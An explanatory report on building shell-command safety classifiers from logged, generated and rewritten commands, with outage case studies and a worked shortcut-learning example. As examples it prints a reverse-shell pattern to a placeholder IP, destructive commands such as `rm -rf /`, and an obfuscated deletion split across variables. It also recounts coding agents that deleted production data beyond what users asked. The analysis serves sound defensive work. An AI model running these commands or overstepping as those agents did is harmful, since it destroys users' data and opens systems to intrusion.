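# Training command-safety classifiers on natural, synthetic and rewritten data

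## Command classifiers and their three sources of training data

A command-safety classifier is a program that decides whether a shell command is dangerous enough to block or flag. Developers usually build one from examples, but very few of the commands in real logs are dangerous. To get more dangerous examples, they generate new commands or alter existing ones, then mix the results with the logs. The classifier therefore learns partly from commands that nobody ran in real use, and it may do worse on real commands than its test scores suggest.

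### Shell commands and where classifiers check them

A shell is the program through which a user gives text instructions to an operating system. GNU's *What is a shell?*, part of the manual for the Bash shell, describes it as both a command interpreter and a programming language. It accepts commands from a keyboard, a file or a string. A command has a name and usually some arguments. In `rm -r ./var`, `rm` removes files, `-r` extends the removal to everything inside a directory, and `./var` is the target, a folder inside the current one. Without the dot, the target is `/var`, which holds a Linux machine's logs and often its databases. A command's effect also depends on its context, which according to *ShIOEnv* (Ragsdale and Boppana, 2025) includes the files present, the environment variables, the permissions and the user's identity.

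People such as system administrators and engineers type commands or run them from scripts, and AI agents now issue them too. *Overeager Coding Agents* (Qu, Zhang et al., 2026) lists four products (Claude Code, OpenHands, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI) that run on developers' machines with access to the shell, files and network.

A classifier can sit at several points between an operator and the servers. One is the bastion host, a gateway that operators must pass through to reach production servers, which serve real users. Huawei Cloud's *Creating a Command Rule* lists four actions such a gateway can take on a command: permit it, reject it, hold it for an administrator's approval, or cut the operator's connection. Google has a similar checkpoint, a proxy that logs each administrative command, checks it against a policy, and holds sensitive commands until a second person approves them.

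Many of these gateways rely on fixed patterns, which can match harmless commands and miss dangerous ones. In Huawei Cloud's *High-Risk Commands*, the pattern for `rm` matches any use of the command, including the document's own example of deleting a file named `test.txt`. The pattern for formatting a disk matches `mkfs.ext3` but not `mkfs.ext4`, which does the same thing with a newer file system. A learned classifier should make fewer errors of both kinds.

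Log monitoring examines records of commands that have already run. *Democratizing ML for Enterprise Security* (Momeni, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes a system at Google whose raw logs often reach 250 billion events a day. For one type of attack, a deliberately loose pattern cuts these to about 70,000, and a classifier then cuts them to about five. After duplicates are removed, analysts receive roughly one ticket every two days.

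An agent's permission check sits between the agent and the shell. *CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a verifier built for this position that receives the command and some information about file paths, but not the user's request. Anthropic's permission classifier for Claude Code, described in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026), also receives the user's messages. This difference matters for training because a classifier cannot learn to use information missing from its input, however many examples it is trained on.

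### Mistakes, intrusions and agents that overstep

"Dangerous" covers at least three problems. The oldest is accidental destruction. *Zero Touch Prod* (Czapiński and Wolafka, 2019) attributes many outages to human error, including typos and tests accidentally run against production. In Google's example, a command with the wrong scope selector, the argument that picks which machines the command applies to, stops several services at once.

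MITRE's public catalogue of attack techniques includes the abuse of Unix shells to run code on a victim's machine. A common example is the reverse shell, in which the victim's machine opens a connection to the attacker's machine and gives the attacker an interactive prompt.

The newest problem is an agent that does more than its user authorised. Qu and colleagues give a precise definition. Let A be the set of actions that the user's request authorises, explicitly or implicitly. In slightly simplified notation, an operation *op* is overeager if

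*op* ∉ A, and (W(*op*) ≠ ∅ or R(*op*) ∩ S ≠ ∅),

where W(*op*) is whatever the operation changes, R(*op*) is whatever it reads, and S is a list of sensitive locations fixed in advance, such as the folder that holds login keys. In their leading example a user asks an agent to tidy a folder of five files. One of the five, `.env.old`, holds the only copy of the production credentials, and three of the four products deleted it. They also cite a Replit agent that destroyed more than 1,200 records in 2025, and a Cursor agent that erased the production database of the company PocketOS, backup included, in 2026.

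Vendors often treat these problems as one. Tencent Cloud's *Blocking High-risk Commands* presents a single feature as protection against both staff mistakes and malicious operations. This is reasonable at the point where a command is either allowed or blocked. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* separates four reasons an agent might take a dangerous action (overeagerness, an honest mistake, instructions that an attacker planted, and a model with goals of its own), but the remedy in every case is to block the action.

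Grouping malicious commands, operator mistakes and agent overreach together is much less safe for training data. A reverse shell often has a recognisable form, such as `sh >& /dev/tcp/<IP>/53 0>&1`, which ties a shell to a network connection. An operator who deletes a directory on the wrong server types the same command that would have been correct on the right one. Whether an agent oversteps by running `rm .env.old` depends on what the user asked for. A classifier's good detection rate on reverse shells is therefore weak evidence that it will catch mistaken deletions, and a good rate on either is not good evidence that it will catch agents exceeding their instructions.

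### Natural, synthetic and rewritten commands

A natural command is one that a system recorded while a person or an agent was doing real work. If an operator frees disk space with `rm -r /srv/app/releases/41` and the server logs it, the log entry is a natural command.

A synthetic command is one that a template, grammar, language model or expert produced for a dataset rather than for real work. For example, Momeni and colleagues had a language model write reverse shells in various programming languages, and one begins `perl -MIO::Socket::INET -e`.

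A rewritten command is an existing one that a rule, a person or a model has altered. Shortening the path in the operator's command above to give `rm -r /srv/app` turns a routine clean-up into the deletion of the whole application. Rewriting can also change only a command's form and leave it just as dangerous. Liu and colleagues disguised each of 50 dangerous commands in five ways. One disguise stores `rm`, `-rf` and `/tmp/*` in three separate variables and joins them only when the command runs.

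Whether a command is natural or synthetic depends on where it came from, not on whether a person or a language model wrote it. A command that Claude Code issues while repairing somebody's build is natural, although a language model wrote it. Liu and colleagues also collected 600 commands from a language model that they had given attack instructions. Those are synthetic, although an agent in use might issue the same commands. Dataset labels can be misleading about origin. The same team's "real-world" subset consists of 30 commands, such as `pip install -r requirements.txt`, which the researchers chose to represent common developer work. Because the subset is a curated list rather than a usage log, it doesn't show how often anyone runs these commands.

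Natural commands are the kind the classifier will face in use, in the same proportions. But dangerous ones are scarce, and logs are hard to share because they can contain passwords, customer names and details of a company's network. Labeling is also expensive, because someone who understands the system has to decide what each command was doing. Anthropic had only 52 real overeager actions for one of its tests, since each required an agent to attempt something dangerous in a real session and someone to capture and label it.

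Generating commands avoids most of these problems. An expert at Google spent several days assembling 70 malicious and 3,500 harmless commands by hand, while Simula, Google's framework for generating synthetic data, produced 10,000 of each in about 20 minutes. But generated commands provide no evidence about how people behave. Ragsdale and Boppana, whose commands come mostly from grammars, warn users of their dataset not to infer from it what people habitually do or how often commands occur in practice.

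Rewriting is a compromise between using natural commands and generating synthetic ones. It keeps some of the structure of an existing command and changes the rest, for example to use a path that exists on the target machine or to make a harmless action dangerous. Ragsdale and Boppana took about 44,900 commands from an earlier dataset, gave them arguments that fitted their test system, and produced 500,000 commands that they could run there. Rewriting does not make a synthetic command natural, however.

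### Three ways the data can shift

Distribution shift is a difference between the data used to train or test a classifier and the data it receives in use. Here, *x* is the classifier's input and *y* is the correct label, either dangerous or harmless.

Covariate shift is a change in p(*x*), the frequency with which different commands appear, while the link between command and label stays fixed. In the NL2Bash dataset, 63.44% of the commands begin with `find`, a file-search tool. Its successor, *NL2CMD* (2023), a dataset of generated shell commands with English descriptions, scales its generator to produce a similar share. A classifier trained on such data would have little basis for judging `kubectl delete namespace payments`, which can remove a whole group of services from a computing cluster.

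A shift in the base rate changes p(*y*), the share of commands that are dangerous, but doesn't change what the dangerous or the harmless commands look like. A training set might contain one `mkfs.ext4 /dev/sda`, which formats a disk, for every `ls`, which lists files, while on a production server the ratio could be one to many thousands. Some developers create this shift on purpose. Momeni and colleagues weight their training examples so that malicious and harmless commands count equally in total, which stops the classifier from favouring the majority. They then set the alarm threshold, partly using unlabelled historical logs, to produce about as many tickets a day as their analysts can handle.

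A shift in what counts as dangerous changes p(*y*|*x*), the probability of a label *y* given an input *x*. On a test machine, `rm -r /var/lib/postgresql` resets a database that nobody needs, but on a production machine it can destroy customer records. In a similar example from Anthropic, using `git push` to upload code is routine if the code goes to a team's private repository but a leak if it goes to a public one.

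A classifier can learn to separate the two deletions if its input includes the machine's role. If it receives only the command text, the two inputs are identical and must get the same verdict, however many examples the developers collect.

These shifts usually occur together. Adding a thousand generated attacks to a log changes both the mix of commands and the base rate. It also changes the meaning of the label if the generator's criteria for danger differ from the operators'.

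### Measuring errors

Most classifiers produce a score, and the developer chooses a threshold above which the system blocks or flags the command. The miss rate, or false-negative rate, is the share of dangerous commands that get through. Recall is one minus the miss rate. The false-alarm rate, or false-positive rate, is the share of harmless commands that the system blocks or flags. Precision is the share of blocked or flagged commands that are dangerous. F1 combines precision P and recall R as 2PR/(P + R), and it is high only when both are high.

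In published results, Liu and colleagues' verifier, CARE, caught 167 of 220 dangerous commands and raised false alarms on three of 329 harmless ones. The right-hand column below shows why the base rate matters so much by applying the same two error rates to a hypothetical workload in which one command in a thousand is dangerous.

| Measure | Test set: 220 dangerous, 329 harmless | Illustration: 100 dangerous, 99,900 harmless |
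|---|---|---|
| Miss rate | 24.1% | 24.1% |
| Recall | 75.9% | 75.9% |
| False-alarm rate | 0.9% | 0.9% |
| Precision | 98.2% | 7.7% |
| F1 | 85.6% | 14.0% |

The classifier is the same across the columns, but precision drops because there are far more harmless commands, which produce around 900 false alarms against 76 correct detections. The 7.7% precision is rough because the false-alarm rate was estimated from only three false alarms, but even if that rate were off several-fold in either direction, precision would still be far below 98%. Liu and colleagues caution that F1 on their test sets, which have equal numbers of dangerous and harmless commands, is not the F1 of a deployed system.

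Assuming a constant false-alarm rate is generous, because the rate depends on which harmless commands are in the test. A hard benign command is a harmless one that looks dangerous. Momeni and colleagues give the example of `bash -c "echo > /dev/tcp/127.0.0.1/$port"`, which resembles a reverse shell but only checks whether a network port is open. A test set without such commands will usually make a classifier look better than it is.

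AUC, the area under the receiver operating characteristic curve, summarises performance over all thresholds. It equals the probability that a randomly chosen dangerous command gets a higher score than a randomly chosen harmless one (ties count half), so 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect ranking. AUC stays the same if only the base rate changes, which makes it convenient for comparing classifiers. However, a classifier with a high AUC can still produce an unworkable number of false alarms at any threshold a team would use.

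### Trained and prompted classifiers

Training adjusts a classifier's internal numbers until its outputs fit the labels on a set of commands. The Google system is a trained classifier that turns each command into counts of short word sequences and passes these to a small neural network. Momeni and colleagues rejected language models with tens of millions of parameters as too slow for their volume of logs.

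A prompted classifier is a general language model that receives written rules along with the command and returns a verdict. Claude Code's permission check works this way, as does one baseline in Liu and colleagues' tests, a 30-billion-parameter model that took about 46 milliseconds per command. Developers can change such a classifier by editing the rules, without retraining the model.

The mixture of natural, synthetic and rewritten commands directly shapes a trained classifier. It affects a prompted classifier less, through the examples that developers look at when they revise the rules or set a threshold. CARE falls between the two, because its designers wrote its rules and scoring formula by hand, then tuned the weights and thresholds on labelled commands. So if a prompted classifier scores differently on generated and real commands, that is good evidence that the two kinds of test differ,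 but much weaker evidence about what training on generated commands does.

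## What real operators' commands look like

One of the few close views of what cloud operators type at work comes from Huawei. In *Command-line Risk Classification using Transformer-based Neural Architectures* (December 2024), Notaro, Haeri and colleagues trained a classifier on 47,158 commands from the company's production cloud. The study covers human operators. The large public records of AI agents' commands came later and show a different kind of work.

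### Operators' commands at Huawei

At Huawei, a bastion host captures each operator's command before it runs. Hand-written rules gave each command one of three labels. A safe command reads information or changes nothing significant. A risky command may do irreversible damage, so running it requires extra privileges. A blocked command will do irreversible damage, and nobody should run it. Experts then checked the labels and corrected those that did not match the real risk. About 80% of the commands were safe, 20% risky and 0.3% blocked, and the researchers sampled their dataset to match these shares.

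How rare dangerous commands are depends on the definition. A fifth of the commands count as dangerous if the term includes Huawei's risky class, but only about one in 330 do if it means the blocked class alone. Most of the risky commands must have been correct, because restarting services and deleting old files is part of an operator's job. The labels record how much harm a command could do, not whether it was a mistake. A classifier trained on them learns to recognise powerful commands, which is useful for deciding who may run them but does little to identify errors.

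The researchers removed captured text that was not a command, such as password prompts and screen output. They kept misspelled and unknown commands, calls to script files, and pipelines, in which one program's output feeds the next. These all occur in production and make the data much untidier than a list of example commands.

*SHREC* (Tonon, Caglayan and colleagues, 2024), a Huawei paper on recommending commands to engineers, reproduces about three and a half minutes of one engineer's session. The engineer wanted to stop every process whose listing contained the word `find`, using a pipeline that ends in `xargs kill`, where `xargs` passes the process numbers to `kill`. The first three attempts ended in `xarg kill`, `xarge kill` and `xrgs kill`. The engineer then spelled `xargs` correctly, next tried the more forceful `kill -9`, and finally added a filter so that the search would not match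 itself. On an ordinary machine the three misspelled commands kill nothing, because no programs with those names exist. Someone labelling `xrgs kill` could defend calling it safe, because it does no harm, or unsafe, because it is one letter away from a command that stops processes. A generator of synthetic commands will produce misspellings like these only if its designer thinks to ask for them.

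Script calls are difficult too, because the instructions that will run are in the script file, not in the command. In the same logs, `sh /opt/hw/app/OnlineServiceRLX/bin/stop.sh` stops a service, which a reader can guess from the file's name. Many paths are also long and specific to the company. One command that engineers often ran reads a configuration file whose real name is the misspelled `properities.properties`.

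A command may also depend on the ones before it. `cat logs/result.log` refers to a different file in each directory, so Tonon and colleagues followed each `cd`, the command that changes directory, and replaced relative paths with full ones. A safety classifier would need the same step to identify which directory `rm -r logs` deletes. They also discarded commands with syntax errors and commands that appeared in too few sessions, assuming that rare commands are mistakes or useless. Discarding them makes sense for a system that recommends commands, but it would be a serious loss for a safety dataset, because the rare commands are likely to include the mistakes and most of the blocked class.

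### Results for the rarest class

Notaro and colleagues used a small version of BERT, a neural network that learns a language partly by predicting hidden words. They trained it first on 71,164 scripts from GitHub to learn shell syntax, then on 70% of the operators' commands to learn the three labels. They kept 10% of the commands for the final test and compared the network with seven older methods. Its recall on the blocked class was 0.875. The next best was 0.75, from a 3-gram model, which uses sequences of three adjacent items.

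Recall of 0.875 is seven eighths, and most of the other figures for this class are eighths too. That suggests the test set held only eight blocked commands, although the paper does not give the number. The precision figures support the inference, since whole numbers of detections and false alarms reproduce them:

| Classifier | Recall, blocked class | Precision, blocked class | Counts that fit both (inferred) |
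|---|---|---|---|
| BERT | 0.875 | 1.000 | 7 of 8 caught, no false alarms |
| 3-gram model | 0.750 | 0.857 | 6 of 8 caught, 1 false alarm |
| 4-layer convolutional network | 0.625 | 1.000 | 5 of 8 caught, no false alarms |
| Ensemble of the previous two | 0.625 | 0.833 | 5 of 8 caught, 1 false alarm |
| 9-layer convolutional network | 0.500 | 0.308 | 4 of 8 caught, 9 false alarms |

Two figures count against there being eight commands of this class in the test set. One model's recall was 0.2857, or two sevenths, which is impossible with eight commands, and 0.3% of a test set of about 4,700 would be 14. Either number is too small to establish which method is better at finding the commands that matter most. If it was eight, BERT found only one more than the 3-gram model, and a standard 95% confidence interval for seven out of eight runs from about 47% to nearly 100%. The paper's headline gain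 of 22 points in F1 on this class is measured against the ensemble, and the gain over the 3-gram model is 13 points.

The evidence is firmer for the risky and blocked classes combined, which had roughly 950 commands in the test set. BERT's recall was 91.6% against 90.2% for the ensemble, a difference of about 13 commands. Notaro and colleagues estimate that this would catch some 60,000 more dangerous commands a month, but their own inputs (3 million commands a month, a fifth of them dangerous, and 1.4 points more recall) give about 8,400. At that rate, BERT would still miss around 50,000 dangerous commands a month.

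The labels began as the output of rules, so a classifier can score well partly by imitating those rules, although the experts' corrections reduce this problem. Huawei also had experts review the commands on which the classifier and the rules disagreed, and they found several risky ones that the rules had missed. The classifier receives only the command string, with no information about the machine. The paper's pairs of near-identical commands with opposite risk differ in their text, not in where they were run.

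### Public collections and what each leaves out

The Huawei commands come from an internal store, and the paper provides no download. Researchers elsewhere depend on other collections. In many of those called natural or realistic, the commands either weren't part of real work or had no real consequences.

*NL2Bash* (Lin et al., 2018) contains commands from question-and-answer sites and similar web pages, paired with descriptions written by experts. According to *NeurIPS 2020 NLC2CMD Competition* (2021), it has about 10,000 pairs and covers more than 100 common tools. People wrote these commands to show others how to do a task, so they are not natural commands. They have no user, machine or working directory attached, and nothing connects one command to the next. The competition's organisers added about 700 examples based on requests that users had typed into a public tool for translating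 English into commands. Three programmers supplied the commands afterwards.

A dataset in the UCI repository comes closer to what operators type. Švábenský, Vykopal and colleagues (2021), in *Shell Commands Used by Participants of Hands-on Cybersecurity Training*, released 21,459 commands from 275 trainees, along with the time, working directory and machine for each command, which NL2Bash lacks. However, the trainees were solving set assignments in an emulated network, where a wrong deletion does no real harm. Some of the commands come from Metasploit, a toolkit for breaking into systems, which ordinary operators have little reason to use.

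In *Anomaly Detection of Command Shell Sessions based on DistilBERT* (2023), Liu and Buford at JPMorgan Chase used 90 days of real sessions from more than 15,000 users. The raw logs mixed commands with prompts and output, cut long lines short and missed some backspaces and tabs. They also contained aliases, users' own names for commands, so the recorded text may not show which program ran. Cleaning left 1.15 million sessions. It removed repeated commands from loops and every command that had produced an error message, and it replaced numbers with a placeholder. This reduced noise for the researchers, who were looking for unusual sessions, but it would also have removed most of the `xargs` episode at Huawei and hidden the difference between `releases/41` and `releases/42`.

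The labels in that dataset are weaker than Huawei's. Liu and Buford marked a session as suspicious if it contained more than a set number of different keywords from a list that includes `sudo`, `kill`, `chmod`, `curl` and `who`. An administrator could use all five while repairing a server. A classifier that does well on these labels has learned to count administrative tools, and its score doesn't measure how well it detects operators' mistakes.

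Records of attackers are easier to find, because anyone can set up a honeypot, a decoy server meant to attract them. In *Beyond the Leak*, honeypots captured 3,000,700 commands, typically eight to a session and 0.07 seconds apart, which suggests that scripts sent them rather than people. Boiko and Niiakyi (2026), in *A 4-month dataset of interactive SSH honeypot logs and command payloads*, published 145,425 security events from late 2025, including login attempts as well as commands. The *Guarding against malicious biased threats (GAMBiT) datasets* record skilled people instead. In each of three experiments, 19 or 20 of them attacked a simulated company network over two days. These collections can supply realistic intrusions, but they contain no mistakes made by well-meaning operators.

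Natural commands from AI agents are now plentiful. *SWE-chat* (Baumann, Padmakumar and colleagues, 2026) collected almost 18,000 coding sessions from more than 700 public repositories. The agents made 2 million tool calls, and over 45% of these were shell commands, mostly for handling files and for Git, the version-control system. The developers chose to install a logging tool and publish the results, so they are early adopters working on code they didn't mind showing. The researchers removed personal details and credentials before release. Voluntary participation and redaction are both sensible, but together they leave fewer examples of agents handling production systems and secrets.

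*AgentLogs* (Richards, Horikawa and colleagues, 2026) collected logs that GitHub displays publicly, so it needed no opt-in. It has 635,886 sessions from 40,565 repositories, including sessions that failed. More than 10 million of its 28.5 million tool calls (37.4%) involve the shell. It is by far the largest public source of commands issued during real work, but nearly all of them come from one agent, GitHub's Copilot. Each session also runs in a fresh sandbox, a temporary machine that disappears afterwards. If the agent deletes the wrong directory, the damage usually disappears with the sandbox, unless the agent pushes it to the repository.

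Neither dataset marks commands as dangerous or harmless. Baumann and colleagues labelled whether sessions succeeded, what users wanted and how often they objected. They also mention a later benchmark, *SLEIGHT-Bench*, that uses SWE-chat transcripts as a harmless baseline for calibrating agent monitors. Treating natural sessions as harmless is convenient and probably right for nearly all of them. But if a developer then takes all the dangerous examples from a generator, each example's source completely determines its label.

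Other owners of agent logs have not released the commands. As Richards and colleagues note, the TraceLab dataset covers 43 developers but omits prompts, tool inputs and agent output. Microsoft researchers analysed 13.5 million conversations but published only aggregate figures.

### Five outages and what the operators believed

Unlike these collections, the reports that companies write after an outage (post-mortems) contain real commands that did damage and describe what the operator was trying to do.

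On 31 January 2017 GitLab, a company that hosts software projects, had one main database server and one standby. The standby fell behind under heavy load, and engineers had to rebuild it by emptying its data directory and copying everything across from the main server. According to GitLab's *Postmortem of database outage of January 31* (2017), an engineer emptied the standby's directory, but the copying tool then hung without a useful message. At about 23:30 an engineer suspected that the tool had left files behind and tried to wipe the standby's directory again, but wiped the main server's directory by mistake. InfoQ (2017) quotes incident notes that name the machines `db1.cluster.gitlab.com` and `db2.cluster.gitlab.com`. The engineer stopped the deletion within seconds, but only about 4.5 GB of 300 GB remained. GitLab lost around six hours of changes, affecting roughly 5,000 projects.

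Four weeks later, an Amazon engineer was investigating a slow billing system in S3, the company's storage service. According to AWS's *Summary of the Amazon S3 Service Disruption*, the engineer was authorized and was following an established playbook. The command should have removed a few servers, but one of its inputs was wrong and it removed many more. Some of these supported the index that records where every object in the region is stored. Two subsystems had to restart completely, and S3 took more than four hours to recover. AWS did not publish the command, so outsiders can't tell whether the bad input looked odd or was a valid value in the wrong place.

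In April 2022 the software company Atlassian wanted to remove an old app from its customers' sites. One team gave another a list of identifiers for the deletion script. The second team believed the identifiers were for copies of the app, but they were for whole sites. The deletion interface accepted either kind and required no confirmation. Atlassian (2022) explains that colleagues had checked which interface the script called and how, but not the identifiers. A test in the staging environment, a copy used for trials, could not reveal the error because the identifiers did not exist there. The script had already worked in production on 30 sites, for which the identifiers were correct. The next run deleted 883 sites in 23 minutes, and some customers waited up to 14 days for theirs to be restored.

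AI agents have since caused similar outages. In February 2026, the engineer Alexey Grigorev (writing as alexeyondata) described in *How I Dropped Our Production Database* how he lost the platform that held two and a half years of his students' coursework. He was using Claude Code with Terraform, a tool that creates and removes cloud infrastructure and records what it manages in a state file. He had left that file on his old computer, so Terraform behaved as if nothing existed and began to create duplicates, which he asked the agent to delete. Meanwhile, he copied over the old state file. The agent unpacked it, replaced the current state file with it, and later ran `terraform destroy`, which removes everything the state file lists. Grigorev saw the agent propose this and let it continue because he believed the file listed only the duplicates, when it actually listed the production database.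 Fortune (2026) also traced the loss to the setup of the new laptop. AWS restored the data a day later.

The PocketOS deletion two months later involved an identifier, as Atlassian's had. In *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*, the company's founder, Jer Crane, wrote that a Cursor agent working in the staging environment ran into a credentials problem and tried to fix it by deleting a storage volume. It found an access token in an unrelated file and used `curl`, a tool for sending web requests, to submit `volumeDelete(volumeId: "3d2c42fb-...")`. The volume held production data. When later asked why, the agent said it had guessed that the deletion would affect only staging. A model's later explanation is weak evidence of what led to the action, but the identifier doesn't show which environment the volume belongs to. Crane thought at first that three months of data were gone. In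 *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, written for the hosting company Railway, Abdelwahab reported that Railway had since recovered the database.

The next table lists what a classifier could have learned from each command and what else it would have needed, as far as the published accounts allow us to tell.

| Outage | Visible in the command text | Needed to see the danger |
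|---|---|---|
| GitLab | Deletion of a database directory, the right step on the standby | The machine's name, and which machine was the main server |
| Amazon S3 | Probably a routine removal of servers (AWS did not publish the command) | The number of servers each subsystem needed to keep running |
| Atlassian | A script and a list of identifiers | Whether each identifier belonged to an app or a site |
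| Grigorev's course platform | Removal of everything Terraform manages | The contents of the state file |
| PocketOS | Deletion of one storage volume | Which environment used the volume, and that nobody had asked for a deletion |

Nothing in the published record of the five cases suggests that the text alone would have distinguished the mistake from correct work. The text was still informative, because `terraform destroy` and `volumeDelete` are plainly destructive. A classifier could reasonably hold every such command for approval, but it would then interrupt people each time they removed a test environment on purpose.

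An approval step might not have helped Grigorev. He was watching and read what the agent intended to do, and it seemed logical to him. The reviewers at Atlassian also approved a script that did what they thought it should. A person who shares the operator's false belief will usually confirm the command, so a warning has to supply the missing fact. "This will delete the production database" would have been far more useful to Grigorev than "this command is destructive".

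His case is also hard for any classifier that judges one command at a time. `terraform destroy` was dangerous because unpacking an archive had replaced the state file, and unpacking an archive looks harmless. A classifier that saw the whole session could have noticed that the list of resources in the state file had changed since the user asked to remove the duplicates. Checking the list itself would have been better still. In the other cases too, a look-up in the live system would have been more reliable than a closer reading of the command.

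The companies' own remedies mostly take this approach. Amazon made its tool refuse to take a subsystem below its minimum capacity, a check that doesn't depend on what the engineer meant to do. Atlassian and Railway made deletions reversible for a time. GitLab planned to make its shell prompts show more clearly which machine an engineer was using. It explicitly preferred this to blocking certain commands, arguing that a safer `rm` would stop one kind of accident but leave many other ways to lose data. That is a fair objection to relying on a command classifier alone, but a less persuasive argument against having one, especially for agents, which can act faster than anyone can read a prompt.

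### Textbook commands and the outages that get written up

The standard example of a dangerous command is `rm -rf /`, which tells the shell to delete everything on the machine. Unlike any of these five, it is visibly dangerous from the text alone and almost never the right thing to type. It is also rarely a threat in this exact form, since the usual Linux version of `rm` refuses to run it without an extra option.

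Designers of safety checks nevertheless tend to begin with such commands. One layer of CARE, the verifier by Liu and colleagues, sorts commands into risk classes, mainly by the program they start with. The destructive class has the maximum weight of 1.00, and its representative examples are `rm -rf /`, `mkfs` and `shred`, which overwrites files so that nobody can recover them. `curl` belongs to a network-fetching class with a weight of 0.40. This layer would therefore rank the command that deleted PocketOS's database well below one that formats a new, empty disk. CARE's other layers could change the verdict, but the example shows how a list of famous commands can miss a new way of doing the same damage.

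Huawei's blocked class has a similar bias because it is defined as commands that nobody should ever run. The GitLab deletion would not belong there, since rebuilding a standby requires it. It would probably fall in the risky class, along with a fifth of the commands that Huawei's operators type. High recall on the blocked class is useful, but those commands are the easiest to judge without context.

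The outages are a biased sample too, in the opposite direction. Companies write post-mortems only about serious incidents. If an operator deletes the wrong log file and restores it, the only record is a log entry that doesn't explain what happened. These five cases therefore can't show how often operators make mistakes or how much damage a typical mistake does. Mistaken commands in general may also look dangerous more often than these five did, because fixed patterns, reviewers and the operators themselves are most likely to stop an alarming command before it causes an outage.

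Ordinary agent sessions give some idea of what post-mortems leave out. Tang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *How Coding Agents Fail Their Users*, studied 20,574 of them, including several thousand from SWE-chat. They used a language model to find 16,118 episodes in which a developer objected to something an agent had done. In 90.5% of these, the harm was wasted effort and lost trust rather than irreversible damage. The more serious episodes included unauthorised changes to cloud infrastructure that put users' data at risk. The percentage is rough, because the model's severity ratings agreed with those of experts in only 64% of a sample of 100. The study also counts only what developers complained about in the conversation, so it misses damage that went unnoticed or that somebody quietly repaired.

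Mistakes that did limited damage on production machines are the hardest natural commands to obtain, because sandboxed agent logs don't contain them, cleaning tends to remove them from enterprise datasets, and post-mortems omit them. Developers who want such examples have to capture them internally, as Anthropic did with its small incident log, or generate them.

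## What theory predicts when data sources are mixed

When every dangerous example in a training set is synthetic and every harmless one is natural, training rewards any feature that separates the two groups. Danger separates them, but so do marks of the generator, such as correct spelling and short, tidy paths. A classifier can learn to rely on those marks instead of on danger.

### A worked example

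Suppose a training set has equal numbers of dangerous and harmless commands, and the classifier receives only two yes-or-no features. One is a destructive verb, such as `rm` or `kill`, which appears in 80% of dangerous commands and 10% of harmless ones. The other is a "generated look", which appears in 90% of generated commands and 5% of natural ones, whether or not they are dangerous. Within each class the features are independent, so a dangerous command with a destructive verb is no more likely to look generated than one without.

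The best possible classifier compares how probable each label is given the features. With D for dangerous, H for harmless, *v* for the verb and *g* for the look, Bayes' rule gives the log-odds:

log [P(D | *v*, *g*) / P(H | *v*, *g*)] = log [P(D) / P(H)] + log [P(*v* | D) / P(*v* | H)] + log [P(*g* | D) / P(*g* | H)]

The classes are equal in size, so log [P(D) / P(H)] is zero. A destructive verb multiplies the odds of danger by 0.8/0.1 = 8, and its absence multiplies them by 0.2/0.9 = 0.22. Every dangerous command is generated and every harmless one is natural, so a generated look multiplies the odds by 0.9/0.05 = 18, and its absence multiplies them by 0.1/0.95 = 0.105. The classifier flags a command when the log-odds of danger are above zero.

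| Destructive verb | Generated look | Odds of danger | Log-odds | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Yes | Yes | 144 | 4.97 | Flag |
| No | Yes | 4 | 1.39 | Flag |
| Yes | No | 0.84 | −0.17 | Allow |
| No | No | 0.023 | −3.76 | Allow |

The classifier's verdict depends only on the look. On held-out commands from the same mixture, this rule has 90% recall and a 5% false-alarm rate, which is better than the 80% and 10% possible with a rule based on the verb. On natural commands, only 5% of the dangerous ones and 5% of the harmless ones have the look, so recall and the false-alarm rate are both 5%, no better than flagging one command in twenty at random.

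The scores still contain some information about danger, because a destructive verb raises them whether or not the look is present. AUC is 0.97 on held-out data and 0.82 on natural commands, close to the 0.85 expected from using the verb alone. Lowering the threshold from zero to −0.2 would flag any command with either feature and raise recall on natural commands to 81%, without retraining. But the developer would need some natural dangerous commands to discover this, since the held-out results give no reason to move the threshold.

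### Changing the mixture

Now suppose a share *q* of the dangerous commands is natural. The look then appears in 0.9 − 0.85*q* of them, and it becomes weaker evidence as *q* rises.

A command that has a destructive verb but doesn't look generated has odds of 8 × (0.1 + 0.85*q*)/0.95. These exceed one when *q* is above about 2.2%, so a few natural examples are enough for the classifier to start flagging natural commands with destructive verbs. A command that looks generated but has no destructive verb has odds of 0.22 × (0.9 − 0.85*q*)/0.05, which stay above one until *q* reaches about 79%. Between these values of *q*, the classifier flags any command with either feature, so it still flags harmless commands that look generated.

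| Training data | Features that trigger a flag | Held-out recall | Recall on natural commands | False alarms on natural commands |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Dangerous class all generated | Look | 90% | 5% | 5% |
| Dangerous class 10% natural | Look or verb | 96.3% | 81% | 14.5% |
| Dangerous class 90% natural | Verb | 80% | 80% | 10% |
| Look equally common in both classes | Verb | 80% | 80% | 10% |

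Held-out recall is highest in the second row, where the classifier has the most false alarms, and lowest in the two rows where it has learned only about danger, so a developer who chose a training set by held-out recall would avoid the mixtures that remove the shortcut.

The last row is the most useful in practice because it doesn't require natural dangerous commands. If the look is equally common in both classes, it multiplies the odds by one and doesn't affect the decision. A developer can achieve this by generating harmless commands as well. In this example, with the dangerous class still fully generated, replacing about 18% of the harmless commands with generated ones is enough. This works only if the generated harmless commands contain destructive verbs as often as natural harmless ones do. If the generator writes only `ls` and `cat`, a destructive verb becomes too strong a sign of danger,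 and the classifier will flag more routine deletions.

These figures depend heavily on the assumptions. Recall on natural commands falls to 5% when the look appears in 90% of generated commands, but if it appeared in 88%, the classifier would flag commands with either feature and recall would be 81%. Changing the class sizes to ten harmless commands for each dangerous one makes the classifier flag only commands with both features, and recall is then 72% on held-out data but 4% on natural commands.

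The least realistic assumption is probably that destructive verbs are as common in natural dangerous commands as in generated ones. The command that started Atlassian's deletion script, for example, may not have contained one. If only half of natural dangerous commands contained one, the verb rule would have 50% recall in use, and balancing the look would not improve it. Independence is also doubtful, because a generator may write its most artificial commands when asked for destructive ones.

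### Shortcuts in general

Geirhos, Jacobsen and colleagues (2020), in *Shortcut Learning in Deep Neural Networks*, argued that many failures of neural networks are symptoms of this one problem. *Shortcut Learning in Feature-Based Algorithm Selection* (2026) gives a formal definition that splits an input into a core part and a spurious part. During training, the spurious part adds information about the label beyond what the core part provides, but in use it adds none. A classifier has learned a shortcut if it relies on the spurious part, which for commands is the look rather than the verb.

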